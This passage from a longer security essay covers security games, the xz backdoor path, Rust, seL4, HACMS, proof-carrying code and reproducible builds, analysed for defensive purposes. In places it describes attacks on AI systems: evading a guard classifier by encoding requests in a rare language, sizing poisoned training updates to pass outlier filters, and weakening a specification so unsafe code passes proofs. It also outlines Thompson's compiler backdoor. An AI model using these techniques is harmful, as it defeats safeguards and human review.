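Baker and colleagues report that competition taught agents skills more relevant to people than a built-in reward for exploring did. They also propose measuring what the agents had learned by giving them new tasks and comparing their results with those of agents trained in other ways or not at all. But these tests covered particular skills in the same kind of simulated world. Even a perfect result would show only that competition teaches skills useful for neighbouring tasks, as with the lemurs, and not that it produces the ability to learn across unrelated domains.

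The experiment therefore suggests that competition favours wider competence when the environment contains more things to use. The hiders and seekers could learn to use boxes and ramps, whereas Go players can only learn to play Go better. The experiment does not show that a system needs this wider competence to resist attack, and the six phases the researchers describe consist mostly of defences that the other team overcame.

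### The case for specialised systems

Generality could also make a system easier to attack. *A case for specialisation in non-human entities* (El-Mhamdi, Hoang and Tighanimine, 2025) argues that it does so in several ways.

Having more parameters can make a model easier to poison when outsiders contribute to its training. The usual defence is to discard contributions that lie far from the rest. Suppose honest contributions vary by about one unit in each parameter. Their typical distance from the average is then the square root of the number of parameters, which is 10 for a model with 100 parameters and 1,000 for a model with a million. The defence has to accept contributions that far away, so a poisoner can push the larger model 1,000 units in a single harmful direction without standing out.

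General models also learn from many kinds of data, much of it collected from the web, and this variety makes malicious examples harder to recognise. Finally, a model that accepts longer inputs gives the attacker more room. The attack that filled part of a prompt with examples of wrong answers depended on this.

This argument is compatible with Bubeck and Sellke's theorem, because a larger model could be both smoother and easier to poison. The theorem concerns how smoothly a model can fit the data it receives, while El-Mhamdi and colleagues are mainly concerned with who can tamper with that data.

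They also discuss Stein's paradox, a statistical argument for generality. For three or more unrelated quantities, a method that combines all the data has a lower expected total error than one that estimates each quantity separately. They accept this, but point out that it assumes the data are safe. If an attacker can corrupt one source, a combined method lets the damage spread to estimates unrelated to that source.

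However, El-Mhamdi and colleagues define generality by the number of tasks that outsiders can ask a system to do. On their definition, a model with trillions of parameters and wide knowledge is specialised if it offers only one service. A spam filter built from a large language model would count as specialised if users could get only "deliver" or "block" from it. Their argument is therefore compatible with premise 5, which concerns what happens inside the system. They also accept that some tasks, such as moderating hate speech correctly, are too hard to specify fully.

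Developers already guard general models with specialised classifiers that check users' requests, the models' answers, or both. Howe and colleagues' results suggest that such a guard could be small. After enough adversarial training, even their smallest classifiers resisted more than 95% of the attacks they had trained against. But the small classifiers coped less well than larger ones when the attack moved to a different part of the text, and the researchers did not test any of them as guards for a larger model.

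An attacker can also get past a small guard by writing a request in a rare language or a simple code that the large model understands and the guard does not, and asking for the answer in the same form. The guard could refuse everything it can't read, but it would also refuse honest people who write in that language. To let their requests through safely, it would have to understand nearly everything the large model does.

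## Security games and limited models of the opponent

Some defenders only have to decide where to look, whereas a guard that reads requests has to understand them. Airport police with fewer dogs than terminals cannot watch every terminal at once, and an attacker who studies the patrols will learn any routine. Game theory, the mathematics of decisions whose results depend on what other people decide, lets the police plan against such an attacker with a model that fits in a small table.

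### One patrol and two targets

In a security game, a defender has to protect several targets with too few guards. The defender first commits to a random schedule, which guards each target t with some probability cₜ. The attacker watches long enough to learn these probabilities, though not where the guards will be on a particular day. He then picks the target with the highest expected gain,

(1 − cₜ) Rₜ + cₜ Pₜ,

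where Rₜ is what he gains if nobody is guarding the target, and Pₜ is what he gets, usually a loss, if somebody is. Researchers call this a Stackelberg game, which means that one side commits first and the other responds. The definition in *Stackelberg vs. Nash in Security Games* (Korzhyk, Yin and colleagues, 2014) requires only that guarding a target always helps the defender and hurts the attacker.

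Suppose a patrol can guard only one of two targets. The first is worth 10 to the attacker if unguarded, the second is worth 5, and a guarded target is worth nothing. If the patrol guards the first target with probability c and the second otherwise, the attacker expects 10(1 − c) from attacking the first and 5c from attacking the second.

| Share of time at the first target | Expected gain from the first | Expected gain from the second | Attacker's best result |
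|---|---|---|---|
| 1/2 | 5 | 2.5 | 5 |
| 2/3 | 10/3 | 10/3 | 10/3 |
| 1 | 0 | 5 | 5 |

The defender does best at c = 2/3, where the two gains are equal. Guarding only the more valuable target is no better than splitting the time evenly.

With the two-thirds schedule, the attacker's expected gain is 10/3 whichever target he picks, so it doesn't matter whether he plans carefully or tosses a coin. If 10 and 5 are the defender's own losses, the defender doesn't need to know what the attacker wants, because the expected loss is 10/3 whichever target is attacked.

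The schedule has to be random. If the patrol guarded the first target two days out of three in a fixed rotation, the attacker would strike on the unguarded day and get 10. The guarantee holds whichever target the attacker chooses, but only on average over the defender's random draws, and a third of his attacks on the first target will still succeed.

A correct prediction can improve on the guarantee. If the defender knows that the attacker always goes for the second target, guarding it all the time reduces the loss to zero. But if the attacker notices and switches, he gets 10.

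The defender may not know whether the attacker has watched the patrols. Korzhyk and colleagues proved that in a large class of these games the defender doesn't need to know, because the best schedule against an attacker who watches is also an equilibrium schedule against one who doesn't. (In an equilibrium, neither side can do better by changing only its own strategy.) This result can fail if the attacker can hit several targets at once.

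### Attackers who make mistakes

Real attackers don't always find the best target. The quantal response model assumes that they choose better targets more often, but not always. If Uᵢ is the expected gain from target i, the probability that the attacker chooses it is

qᵢ = e^(λUᵢ) / Σ e^(λUⱼ),

where the sum covers all the targets. The number λ measures how reliably he picks the best one. At λ = 0 he chooses at random, and as λ grows he approaches a perfect attacker. In the example, an even split gives him 5 from the first target and 2.5 from the second. With λ = 0.5, he attacks the first about 78% of the time.

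A defender who is sure of that value of λ can lower the expected loss from the guaranteed 3.33 to about 3.28 by guarding the first target 71% of the time. But a perfect attacker would then attack the second target and raise the expected loss to 3.55, so the defender risks more than it gains.

People may also not weigh risks and rewards as the formula for expected gain does. Nguyen, Yang and colleagues (2013), in *Analyzing the Effectiveness of Adversary Modeling in Security Games*, replaced Uᵢ with a weighted sum,

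w₁cᵢ + w₂Rᵢ + w₃Pᵢ,

and learned the weights from people's choices in a game. They came out at −9.85, 0.37 and 0.15. Raising the chance of a guard by ten percentage points therefore put these players off a target about as much as cutting its reward by 2.7 points, in games where rewards went up to 10.

### Tests on human players

*Improving resource allocation strategies against human adversaries in security games* (Yang, Kiekintveld and colleagues, 2013) describes an online treasure-hunting game modelled on the eight terminals of Los Angeles International Airport. Guards protect three of eight gates. The player sees each gate's reward, penalty and probability of being guarded, then chooses one to open. Guard schedules based on quantal response earned the defender more than the previous best method.

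A method called MATCH then did better without any model of how people choose. It ensures that if an attacker departs from his best choice, the defender loses no more than a fixed multiple of what the attacker loses. This raised the question of whether it was worth modelling the attacker at all.

Nguyen and colleagues tried to answer it with 547 people, who played 11,102 games. The weighted model's predictions fitted the players' choices in 51 of 100 test settings, compared with 8 for plain quantal response. Adding two more weighted terms, the defender's own reward and penalty, reduced the number to 44. In 22 further settings, schedules based on the three-weight model beat MATCH significantly in 13 and lost in one. But when the researchers gave MATCH the same weighted sum and tuned its multiple, the three-weight schedules won in only five settings and lost in three. The researchers had also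 chosen settings in which the methods recommended different schedules, so the differences in performance may be smaller in general.

Most of the players were paid online workers, but some were current and former members of an Israeli intelligence unit, who chose more rationally. Against them, the weighted model still did better than assuming a perfect attacker, but its lead over MATCH was smaller.

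The model that predicts attacks best may not produce the best schedule, because errors about a target matter little if correcting them would not change where guards are placed. *End-to-End Game-Focused Learning of Adversary Behavior in Security Games* (2019) reanalysed data from these experiments and trained a model to improve the defender's result directly, instead of training it to predict choices first. The defender earned more this way, except in the eight-target version when there were fewer than ten training games.

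### Airports, harbours and wildlife parks

The airport police in Los Angeles have used a program called ARMOR since August 2007 to schedule road checkpoints and dog patrols. Before ARMOR, they ran one checkpoint a day, left it in place all day, and followed a fixed sequence that an observer could have learned. Pita, Jain and colleagues (2009) write in *Using Game Theory for Los Angeles Airport Security* that the police can override ARMOR's schedules. Taylor, Kiekintveld and colleagues (2010) report in *A Framework for Evaluating Deployed Security Systems* that the police had not chosen to do so.

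Taylor and colleagues calculated that three dogs on ARMOR's schedule protect the terminals better than six dogs assigned evenly at random. The calculation assumes that attackers behave as the model predicts and that experts estimated the payoffs correctly. Quadrupling one of those estimates, the harm from a successful attack, hardly changed the checkpoint schedules.

There is little evidence from outside the model. In January 2009, seven stops at the checkpoints turned up firearms. Taylor and colleagues call this encouraging but not conclusive. They give no figure for earlier months, and a larger budget had also paid for more checkpoints. Nobody knows how many weapons got through or how many attackers stayed away.

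The US Coast Guard began using a similar program, PROTECT, in Boston in April 2011. The paper *PROTECT* (An, Shieh and colleagues, 2012) describes it as the first such system in use to assume quantal response. A risk analysis company estimated the damage from an attack on each target. Coast Guard experts thought λ could lie anywhere in a broad range, so the researchers considered values from 0.5 to 4 and chose 1.5, which gave the best average result across that range.

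According to patrol records, the Coast Guard patrolled much less on one day of the week than on the others before PROTECT, and that gap disappeared afterwards. Boats also visited the more valuable areas consistently. One user asked whether the program was broken, because in 60 days it had scheduled no patrol to start at 4 a.m. or 4 p.m. Such gaps are expected, because a program that picks 60 start times at random from 24 equally likely hours will miss about two of those hours on average.

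It is harder to tell whether Boston became safer. A team of mock attackers judged that the patrols had become a better deterrent, but the same team had helped shape PROTECT. Crews reported more illicit activity than before, but they had also received better guidance on how to patrol. New York adopted the system in 2012, and The Maritime Executive's *USC Engineered AntiTerrorism System Deployed at Ports of Los Angeles* reports that the Los Angeles and Long Beach ports followed.

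Waiting for attacks would not settle whether patrols work. Suppose a port suffers one attack every 20 years on average, and new patrols halve that rate. The chance of a decade without attacks is then 61% with the old patrols and 78% with the new ones, so a quiet decade is only weak evidence that the new patrols work.

Poaching is much more common, which makes it easier to study. PAWS, the Protection Assistant for Wildlife Security, uses records of snares and other signs of poaching to plan rangers' patrols. In field tests in Uganda and Cambodia, rangers found more of these signs where the models had predicted high risk than where they had predicted low risk. This is better evidence than the other two systems have. It shows that the predictions were useful, but it does not show that poaching fell.

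### Poker without reading the opponent

Poker is a clearer test because players can finish thousands of hands and count their winnings. In January 2017, the program Libratus beat four top professionals over 120,000 hands of heads-up no-limit Texas hold'em, a two-player game in which players may bet any amount up to all their chips. The game has about 10¹⁶¹ decision points, according to *Super-Human AI for Strategic Reasoning*.

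The poker program Libratus relied on much the same guarantee as the two-thirds patrol, rather than on reading its opponents. In a two-player game where one side wins what the other loses, a player who follows an equilibrium strategy and takes each seat equally often cannot lose on average to anyone. Brown and Sandholm's *Superhuman AI for heads-up no-limit poker* describes how Libratus approximated such a strategy. The program first solved a simplified version of the game to get a blueprint strategy that was detailed for the early rounds and rough for the later ones. When play reached a later round, it worked out a finer strategy for the rest of that hand.

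PSC's *CMU Group Describes “Superhuman” Poker AI in Science* (2017) reports that Libratus used the professionals' play to repair weaknesses in its own strategy during the competition. For instance, it added responses to bet sizes that the professionals had used but the blueprint lacked. These repairs did not require a model of any particular professional.

In 2019, Brown and Sandholm's program Pluribus beat professionals at six-player poker, also without adapting to individual opponents. With more than two players, an equilibrium strategy no longer guarantees that a player won't lose on average, so Pluribus's success is evidence about poker in practice rather than a consequence of the theory.

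A program that plays this way wins less from a weak opponent than a player who exploits that opponent's mistakes, but a defender can usually accept this. KataGo's losses show that practice against copies of oneself is not enough to get close to an equilibrium.

### Moves that nobody listed

ARMOR, PROTECT and Libratus all depend on someone describing the game beforehand. Suppose the defender in the first example has overlooked a third target, worth 8. No patrol ever goes there, so an attacker who finds it can expect 8 instead of 10/3. The defender can't detect the omission from the calculation, because it is still correct for the two listed targets.

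Security games suit ports and airports because targets such as bridges and terminals are hard to overlook, and an attacker has to go to them. The list of targets can also stay short because it doesn't have to include every method of attack. A patrol near a ferry terminal may stop an attacker whether he comes with a bomb or a stolen boat, as long as the estimate of how well patrols work is accurate for both. Even in this setting, An and colleagues left coordinated attacks for future work.

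In poker, the opponent's possible moves are listed in the rules. If a professional makes a bet that the blueprint left out, it is still an amount of money, so Libratus can calculate its consequences. Someone planting a backdoor has much more freedom. A project that divided its review time among xz's source files could have followed its schedule perfectly and still missed the line that existed only in the release archives. To include the archives, somebody would have had to realise that they could differ from the source code.

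Premise 3 therefore holds for PROTECT only in a very limited sense. While PROTECT runs, it represents the attacker's goals as a table of payoffs and his skill as a single number, much like the spam filter that calculated a spammer's costs. Analysts, boat crews and mock attackers supplied the broader understanding when they drew up the table. If attackers keep finding new kinds of target, people will have to keep supplying that understanding.

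### Choosing which changes to inspect

Part of the method works in code review without a list of attacks, because a project can list the submissions instead. If it randomly chooses which changes to inspect deeply, and chooses only after they arrive, a contributor can't arrange to avoid inspection. This applies equally to tricks nobody has thought of, provided they are in something the project inspects.

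The project can also give more attention to sensitive code. Suppose it receives 400 changes a year and can inspect 100 of them deeply. A backdoor would do 10 units of harm in any of the 100 changes to sensitive code, and 5 in any of the other 300. Suppose also, for now, that a deep inspection always finds a backdoor. If every change is equally likely to be inspected, an attacker who targets sensitive code can expect to do 7.5 units of harm. If the project inspects all the sensitive changes, he can target the other code and do 5. The best plan is to inspect about 57 of the sensitive changes and 43 of the others, chosen at random, which limits his expected harm to about 4.3 units whichever kind of code he targets.

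Recent papers apply such games to software and AI. *VCAO* (2026) treats the search for flaws in operating-system kernels as a Stackelberg game and makes the file rankings that Anthropic's researchers used with Mythos Preview part of that game. *Beyond Best Response* (2026) applies quantal response to deceptive defences, such as decoys, to protect against a wrong model of the attacker.

Kim, Choo and colleagues (2026), in *Incentive-Aware AI Safety via Strategic Resource Allocation*, propose random audits of the people who label training data for language models. With a fixed rule about whose work to recheck, a dishonest labeller could learn when he was safe. They plan for an attacker who knows the audit policy because a policy that withstands him is likely to withstand someone who knows less. They also propose using security games to divide reviewers among subjects such as medicine and coding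 when testing a model, but acknowledge that it is unclear how to list a weakness that arises from several steps together. The xz backdoor, which had two parts, was a weakness of this kind.

Random inspection may also deter attackers less in software than at an airport, where someone caught with a bomb goes to prison. Let G be what an attacker gains from a successful backdoor and C what he loses if the project catches him. If the chance of catching him is 5%, the attempt is worthwhile unless

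0.95G − 0.05C < 0,

which requires C to be more than 19 times G. An attacker who used a false name may lose only the name and the work he put into it.

Inspection is also useless if the inspector doesn't recognise the backdoor. Wu and Lu estimated that kernel maintainers catch about 19% of one kind of memory flaw. If deep inspections did no better, the project in the example could inspect every sensitive change and still expect 8.1 units of harm from an attack there, compared with 10 if it inspected none. No schedule within its budget would reduce the expected harm further, so the project would need better inspectors.

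## Shrinking what an attacker can reach

A project can also leave attackers fewer places to put a backdoor, which helps if inspectors often fail to recognise one. A system's attack surface is the set of all points where an attacker can supply input to it or otherwise act on it. Removing one of these points stops every attack that depends on it, including attacks nobody has thought of.

### The ssh server before and after xz

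The xz backdoor reached Debian's ssh server through code that the server hardly needed. When the server starts, it notifies systemd, the program that manages services on most Linux systems, that it is ready. The notification is a short piece of text, but Debian's version of the server loaded a whole library, libsystemd, to send it. Because libsystemd can also read compressed log files, it loaded liblzma, the xz library. In *Debian openssh option review*, Watson (2024) wrote that using an existing library had seemed a reasonable trade-off when he added it to the package. In the same discussion, Miller (2024) recalled that someone had attacked the ssh server through an indirect dependency about ten years earlier.

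Developers have since removed this path and several others:

| Part of the server | Early 2024 | Late August 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Notifying systemd | Uses libsystemd, which loads liblzma | Uses a little code of the server's own |
| Accepting connections | One program that also handles the SSH protocol | A small separate program that doesn't handle the protocol |
| GSS-API, a login method for organisations with central accounts | In the standard package | In a separate package in Debian's development version |

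Before anyone knew about the backdoor, the systemd developers had made a change that would have blocked it. According to a reply to Freund's report, a contributor proposed on 29 February 2024 to load compression libraries only when needed, and the project merged the change on 5 March, more than three weeks before Freund's discovery became public. The contributor wanted to make the files that start a computer smaller. According to bluca (2024), in *A backdoor in xz*, the change makes libsystemd load a compression library only when a program asks it to read a log file compressed in that format. The ssh server never does, so the change would have protected it without anyone having to suspect Jia Tan. The reply speculates that the attackers may have hurried because of the change.

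The OpenSSH project added its own notification code to the server in version 9.8. djm (2024) wrote in *nit* that the developers would have done so sooner if someone had published a specification, but other commenters replied that the documentation had existed for years. One of them also claimed that part of the new code did not work, which is a risk whenever a project replaces a library with its own code.

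The release notes from OpenSSH (2024) also describe a critical flaw in the server itself. In laboratory tests on 32-bit Linux, an attacker who kept connecting for six to eight hours could run commands as root. Removing liblzma would not have prevented this flaw.

GSS-API took longer to remove. Watson had added part of it in 2005 with a patch of about 4,000 lines. OpenSSH's developers had always rejected the patch because it exposed more code to people who hadn't logged in. In 2026, Debian reported a flaw in the patch that a remote attacker could use to disrupt servers with the feature turned on, and possibly to run code on them. That August, Debian moved GSS-API to a separate package in its development version. Once a stable release includes this change, servers that upgrade will no longer contain the code, or any undiscovered flaws in it, unless their administrators install the separate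 package.

### What a memory-safe compiler refuses

Some programming languages prevent a whole class of flaws in every program written in them. In Rust, each piece of data has one owner, and the program releases the memory when the owner no longer needs it. Other parts of the program can borrow the data, but the compiler refuses any program in which a borrower might use it after its release. For example, it rejects these lines:

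```
let name = String::from("Ada");
let view = &name;
drop(name);
println!("{}", view);
```

The second line creates a reference to the text, the third releases the text, and the fourth tries to print it through the reference. This is a use-after-free, the kind of flaw that Wu and Lu planted in their hypocrite commits. Kernel maintainers often miss such flaws, but Rust's compiler rejects all of them in ordinary Rust, regardless of who wrote the code or why. The compiler usually can't determine in advance whether a program will read past the end of a list, so it adds a check that stops the program if this happens. An attacker may still be able to crash the program but can't use the mistake to read or change other memory.

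Like other sound checkers, the compiler rejects some harmless programs. It normally won't let a program hold two references at once, one for changing the first item of a list and one for changing the second, because it does not determine that the items are different. The programmer can rewrite the code, or mark a section as "unsafe" and take responsibility for what the compiler cannot check.

Google has used Rust for much of the new code in Android. Google (2024) reported that memory-safety flaws fell from 76% of Android's vulnerabilities to 24% over six years. Vander Stoep (2025), in *Rust in Android*, put the 2025 share below 20%. A share can also fall because people find more flaws of other kinds, so flaws per line of code are a better measure. Vander Stoep counts one potential memory-safety vulnerability in about five million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million, compared with roughly 1,000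 per million in Android's older C and C++ code.

One flaw is very little data. If the true rate in Rust were 1.1 per million lines, five million lines would still contain at most one flaw about 2.5% of the time. Even that rate would be about 900 times lower than the rate for C and C++. The comparison may overstate Rust's advantage somewhat, because people have had longer to search the older code.

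The one flaw was in an unsafe section of a program that reads images, and Google fixed it before release. Android's memory allocator, which puts inaccessible regions around large blocks of memory, would have stopped an attacker from exploiting the flaw. About 4% of Android's Rust code is in unsafe sections, so reviewers looking for memory errors can concentrate on those.

### Proving a kernel correct

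Memory safety rules out certain mistakes. A machine-checked proof can go further and show that a program meets its specification. The best-known program with such a proof is seL4, a small operating-system kernel. A kernel controls which programs can use which memory and devices, so a flaw in it can give an attacker access to everything else.

Let B(C) be the set of everything the kernel's C code can do, and B(S) the set of everything its specification allows. The central proof shows that

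B(C) ⊆ B(S).

If nothing in B(S) lets a program change data without permission, then nothing in the code does either, whatever input an attacker chooses. *Formally Verified Software in the Real World* describes further proofs that no program can gain more permissions than the system's policy allows, or learn another program's data without permission. On some processors, the proofs extend from the C code to the machine code, so users don't have to trust the compiler.

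seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists the assumptions the proofs rely on. The hardware has to work correctly, and devices that can write directly to memory must not overwrite the kernel. About 340 lines of assembly code (on ARM processors) and 1,200 lines of start-up code also have to be correct. The proof about secrets does not cover timing, so how long one program takes might still reveal information to another.

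The seL4 project reports that nobody has found a case where the kernel's verified code departs from its specification in more than 15 years. Over the same period, its developers have found small defects in every kind of unverified code in the kernel. The project is reporting on its own work, but outside researchers got a similar result with CompCert, a C compiler with a correctness proof. They spent about six years of processor time trying to make it produce wrong code and found no such errors in the version then under development, though they had found them in every other compiler they tested.

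Andronick warns in *What's verified, what's not, and what does it mean?* that downloading seL4 does not give someone a verified system. They have to use a configuration that the proofs cover, set it up correctly and verify any other critical parts.

### A helicopter with an attacker on board

DARPA's HACMS programme tested whether a verified kernel could protect a larger system that contained unverified software. The system was the Unmanned Little Bird, a Boeing helicopter that can fly itself. In 2013, professional penetration testers took control of its software and could have crashed it or sent it anywhere. Boeing's engineers then rebuilt the mission computer, which communicates with the ground and directs the flight computer. Klein and colleagues describe a simplified version of the process:

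1. The engineers ran the existing software unchanged on top of seL4, inside a virtual machine (a simulated computer). This added no security, but made the next step possible.
2. They split the software into separate virtual machines, with only the necessary communication between them.
3. They rewrote the critical parts, including the encryption, in a language that prevents memory errors. The camera software stayed on ordinary Linux.
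4. They analysed the security of the whole system, assuming that an attacker might already control the camera.

The testers had the source code, and Fisher reports in *DARPA's HACMS Program* that they had attended the design meetings. They also had full control of the camera's part of the system, but according to DARPA's *HACMS*, in six weeks they could neither break out of that part nor disrupt the flight. They failed again when they attacked the helicopter while it was flying with people on board.

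The designers assumed that someone would break into the camera software, so they didn't need to predict how. An attacker who did so could still send false pictures or positions to the rest of the mission computer, which therefore had to check what it received.

The attackers' six-week failure is good evidence, because similar attackers had easily succeeded before the changes, but it does not show that no attack exists. DARPA writes that mathematics guaranteed the attackers would remain trapped, but Klein and colleagues acknowledge that the link between the kernel's proofs and the security of the whole system was still informal. Their analysis of a similar quadcopter also left out radio jamming. *UAV Resilience Against Stealthy Attacks* (2025) describes a kind of attack on drones that also threatens the HACMS approach.

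### Making the supplier prove it

A system may also have to run code from strangers. George Necula and Peter Lee developed proof-carrying code for this case in the 1990s. The supplier has to prove that the code is safe, and the receiver only has to check the proof.

Suppose an operating system lets users supply small programs that examine network packets. A packet has n bytes, numbered from 0 to n − 1, and a program may read only those bytes. The process works as follows:

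1. The receiver publishes the rule, here that a program may read byte i only if 0 ≤ i < n.
2. The supplier uses a standard procedure to turn the program into a logical formula that is true only if the program obeys the rule.
3. The supplier proves the formula and sends the program with the proof.
4. The receiver works out the formula again from the program it received, and checks that the proof fits.

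If the program reads byte i without checking its value, the formula states that 0 ≤ i < n for every i, which is false, so no valid proof exists. If the program first tests whether i is in range, the formula becomes

(0 ≤ i < n) implies (0 ≤ i < n),

which is easy to prove. An attacker who alters the program on the way changes the formula too, and the old proof will fit only if the altered program is still safe.

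The receiver must still trust its own checker. The Linux kernel's eBPF verifier checks small programs that users supply, but it analyzes each program for safety itself instead of receiving a proof. Attackers have exploited mistakes in the verifier to take over computers.

### A backdoor that is missing from the source

All of these checks can fail if the program that runs differs from the one somebody checked. In a reproducible build, anyone who compiles the same source code with the same tools gets the same file, down to the last bit. Several people can then build the program independently and compare their files. If one build machine has added a backdoor, its file will differ from the others.

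Developers first have to remove harmless differences between builds, such as the date and time that many tools write into their output. The method also assumes that everyone starts from source code free of malicious code. Everyone who built from the xz release archive, for example, would have got the same backdoor. OpenSSH now puts its generated files in the repository, so the signed release branch should exactly match the release archive.

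Reproducible builds also miss a backdoor in the compiler that everyone uses. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, explained in his 1984 Turing Award lecture how to hide one:

1. The attacker changes a compiler's source code so that it adds a secret password whenever it compiles the login program.
2. Because anyone could see this change in the source, he adds another. When the compiler compiles a new copy of itself, it inserts both changes into the copy.
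3. He compiles this source code and installs the result.
4. He restores the original, clean source code.

From then on, the installed compiler compiles its own clean source into another infected compiler. A reviewer could read every line of source code for the compiler and the login program and find nothing, however intelligent the reviewer was.

David A. Wheeler, who also studied the underhanded programs, developed a check called diverse double-compiling. Let A be the suspect compiler, s its source code and T a second compiler by someone else. Write A(s) for the file that A produces from s. The check has four steps:

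1. Compile s with A, and confirm that A(s) is identical to A.
2. Compile s with T to get a new compiler, X = T(s). X will differ from A because T translates code in its own way, but it should behave as s specifies.
3. Compile s again with X to get Y = X(s).
4. Compare Y with A.

If A is clean, then A and X are both translations of s. They should do the same thing with any input, including s, so Y and A should be identical. If A is infected and T isn't, X and Y are both clean, so Y will differ from A.

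T can be slow or have unrelated bugs, as long as it compiles s correctly and does not contain the same trick. The attacker would have to infect both A and T, and the defender can choose T after the attack. Wheeler applied the check to GCC, a widely used compiler, with Intel's compiler as T, and also used it to expose a deliberately infected Lisp compiler. A match shows only that A corresponds to its source, so someone still has to review the source.

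### Language models as builders

Writing proofs and rewriting old programs used to require scarce experts, but language models can now do some of this work. The 2025 vericoding benchmark contains about 12,500 specifications. For each one, a model has to write a program and a proof that the program meets the specification. Off-the-shelf models succeeded on 82% of the tasks in the Dafny language, 44% in Verus, which checks Rust programs, and 27% in Lean. The tasks differ between languages, and most are far smaller than a kernel. Newer models would probably do better.

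Translations of old code are harder to check, because a translation can pass every test and still behave differently from the original on an input an attacker chooses. A faithful translation will also keep any logic mistakes in the original. CRUST-Bench, also from 2025, measures whether a model can translate each of 100 C projects into safe Rust that passes a set of tests. OpenAI's o1 succeeded on 15 at the first attempt.

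If the proof checker is sound and the specification is right, even a malicious language model can't write a proof that gets an unsafe program accepted. But if the model also writes the specification, it can make the specification too weak. For example, the specification for a sorting program might require only that each item in the output is no larger than the next. An empty list meets this requirement, so a program that throws away all the data could pass.

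These methods move much of the need for general cognition from reviewing to building. Checking a proof or comparing two files is narrow work, but people needed broad understanding to design Rust's rules and to split up the helicopter's software. They could choose designs that were easy to verify, whereas a reviewer has to judge whatever an attacker submits. A builder who fails to find a proof loses time but doesn't let an attack through. Some of the building is narrow too, since automatic provers did the last step of the seL4 proofs, from C to machine code. Nobody has shown that a prover trained only on proofs would fail at the rest, so the success of language models doesn't show that it requires general cognition.

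### What the rules leave out

A specification can omit something its writers would have wanted. A specification for John Meacham's program that required only a black rectangle would have had this flaw. According to seL4, users may also expect things of the kernel that its proofs don't cover, and the kernel's developers run tests partly to check whether the specification matches what they intended.

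Several flaws that Debian listed for OpenSSH in 2026 were logic errors in permitted functions. If an administrator allowed one type of ECDSA login key, the server accepted the other types as well. A setting meant to restrict what a key could do did not apply to one kind of network tunnel. Rust's compiler would not reject either mistake, because neither involves misusing memory. A proof could have ruled them out, but only if someone had first written down what each setting should do.

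An attacker can also persuade people to change the rules. Someone in Jia Tan's position could propose a new permission for a feature that users want, or a new dependency that saves work. Once the permission was granted, a proof checker would correctly accept code that used it. Reviewers would have less to read, but they would have to judge whether the person proposing the change was honest, as premise 3 describes.

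Hardware can fail in ways the seL4 proofs don't consider. In an attack called Rowhammer, a program reads the same memory cells so often that bits flip in neighbouring cells it has no permission to change. In Spectre, which researchers disclosed in 2018, a program uses timing to learn secrets that the processor handled while guessing what to do next. Both attacks break assumptions behind the proofs, so correct kernel code is not enough to stop them.

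The approach is weakest for services that have to accept whatever people write. A moderation program can run on a verified kernel and still miss a dog whistle. Isolation can limit the damage from such mistakes. If a program that reads email can't send messages or open files, a deceptive email can't make it send out a password. But the email can still cause the program to give its user a false summary, and no rule about memory or permissions would prevent that.

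### Who pays

Users lose features when developers remove code. An organisation that relies on GSS-API will have to install a separate package when it upgrades Debian, and an administrator who misses the announcement could be locked out of a remote machine. In *Free software activity in March 2026* (2026), the package's maintainer looked forward to the split but expected to keep maintaining the GSS-API code. Loading libraries only when needed also makes work for packagers, because their tools no longer detect those dependencies automatically. The systemd developers had to add a new kind of label to their programs to compensate.

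Rewriting and verifying code takes a lot of work. DARPA's researchers rewrote about 80,000 of the quadcopter's 100,000 lines of code. The original proof of seL4, a kernel of roughly 10,000 lines, took about 20 person-years, including the time spent creating tools and methods. Changing verified code may also require repairing the proof.

Rust can save effort once programmers know it. Vander Stoep reports that Android's developers spend about 25% less time reviewing Rust changes than C++ changes, and that they roll back medium and large ones about a quarter as often. But Google can pay to train its programmers, and these figures come mainly from new code. A volunteer who maintains an old C library alone, as Lasse Collin did with xz, would have to learn Rust and rewrite the library before saving any effort, and might have to accept help from strangers to do it.
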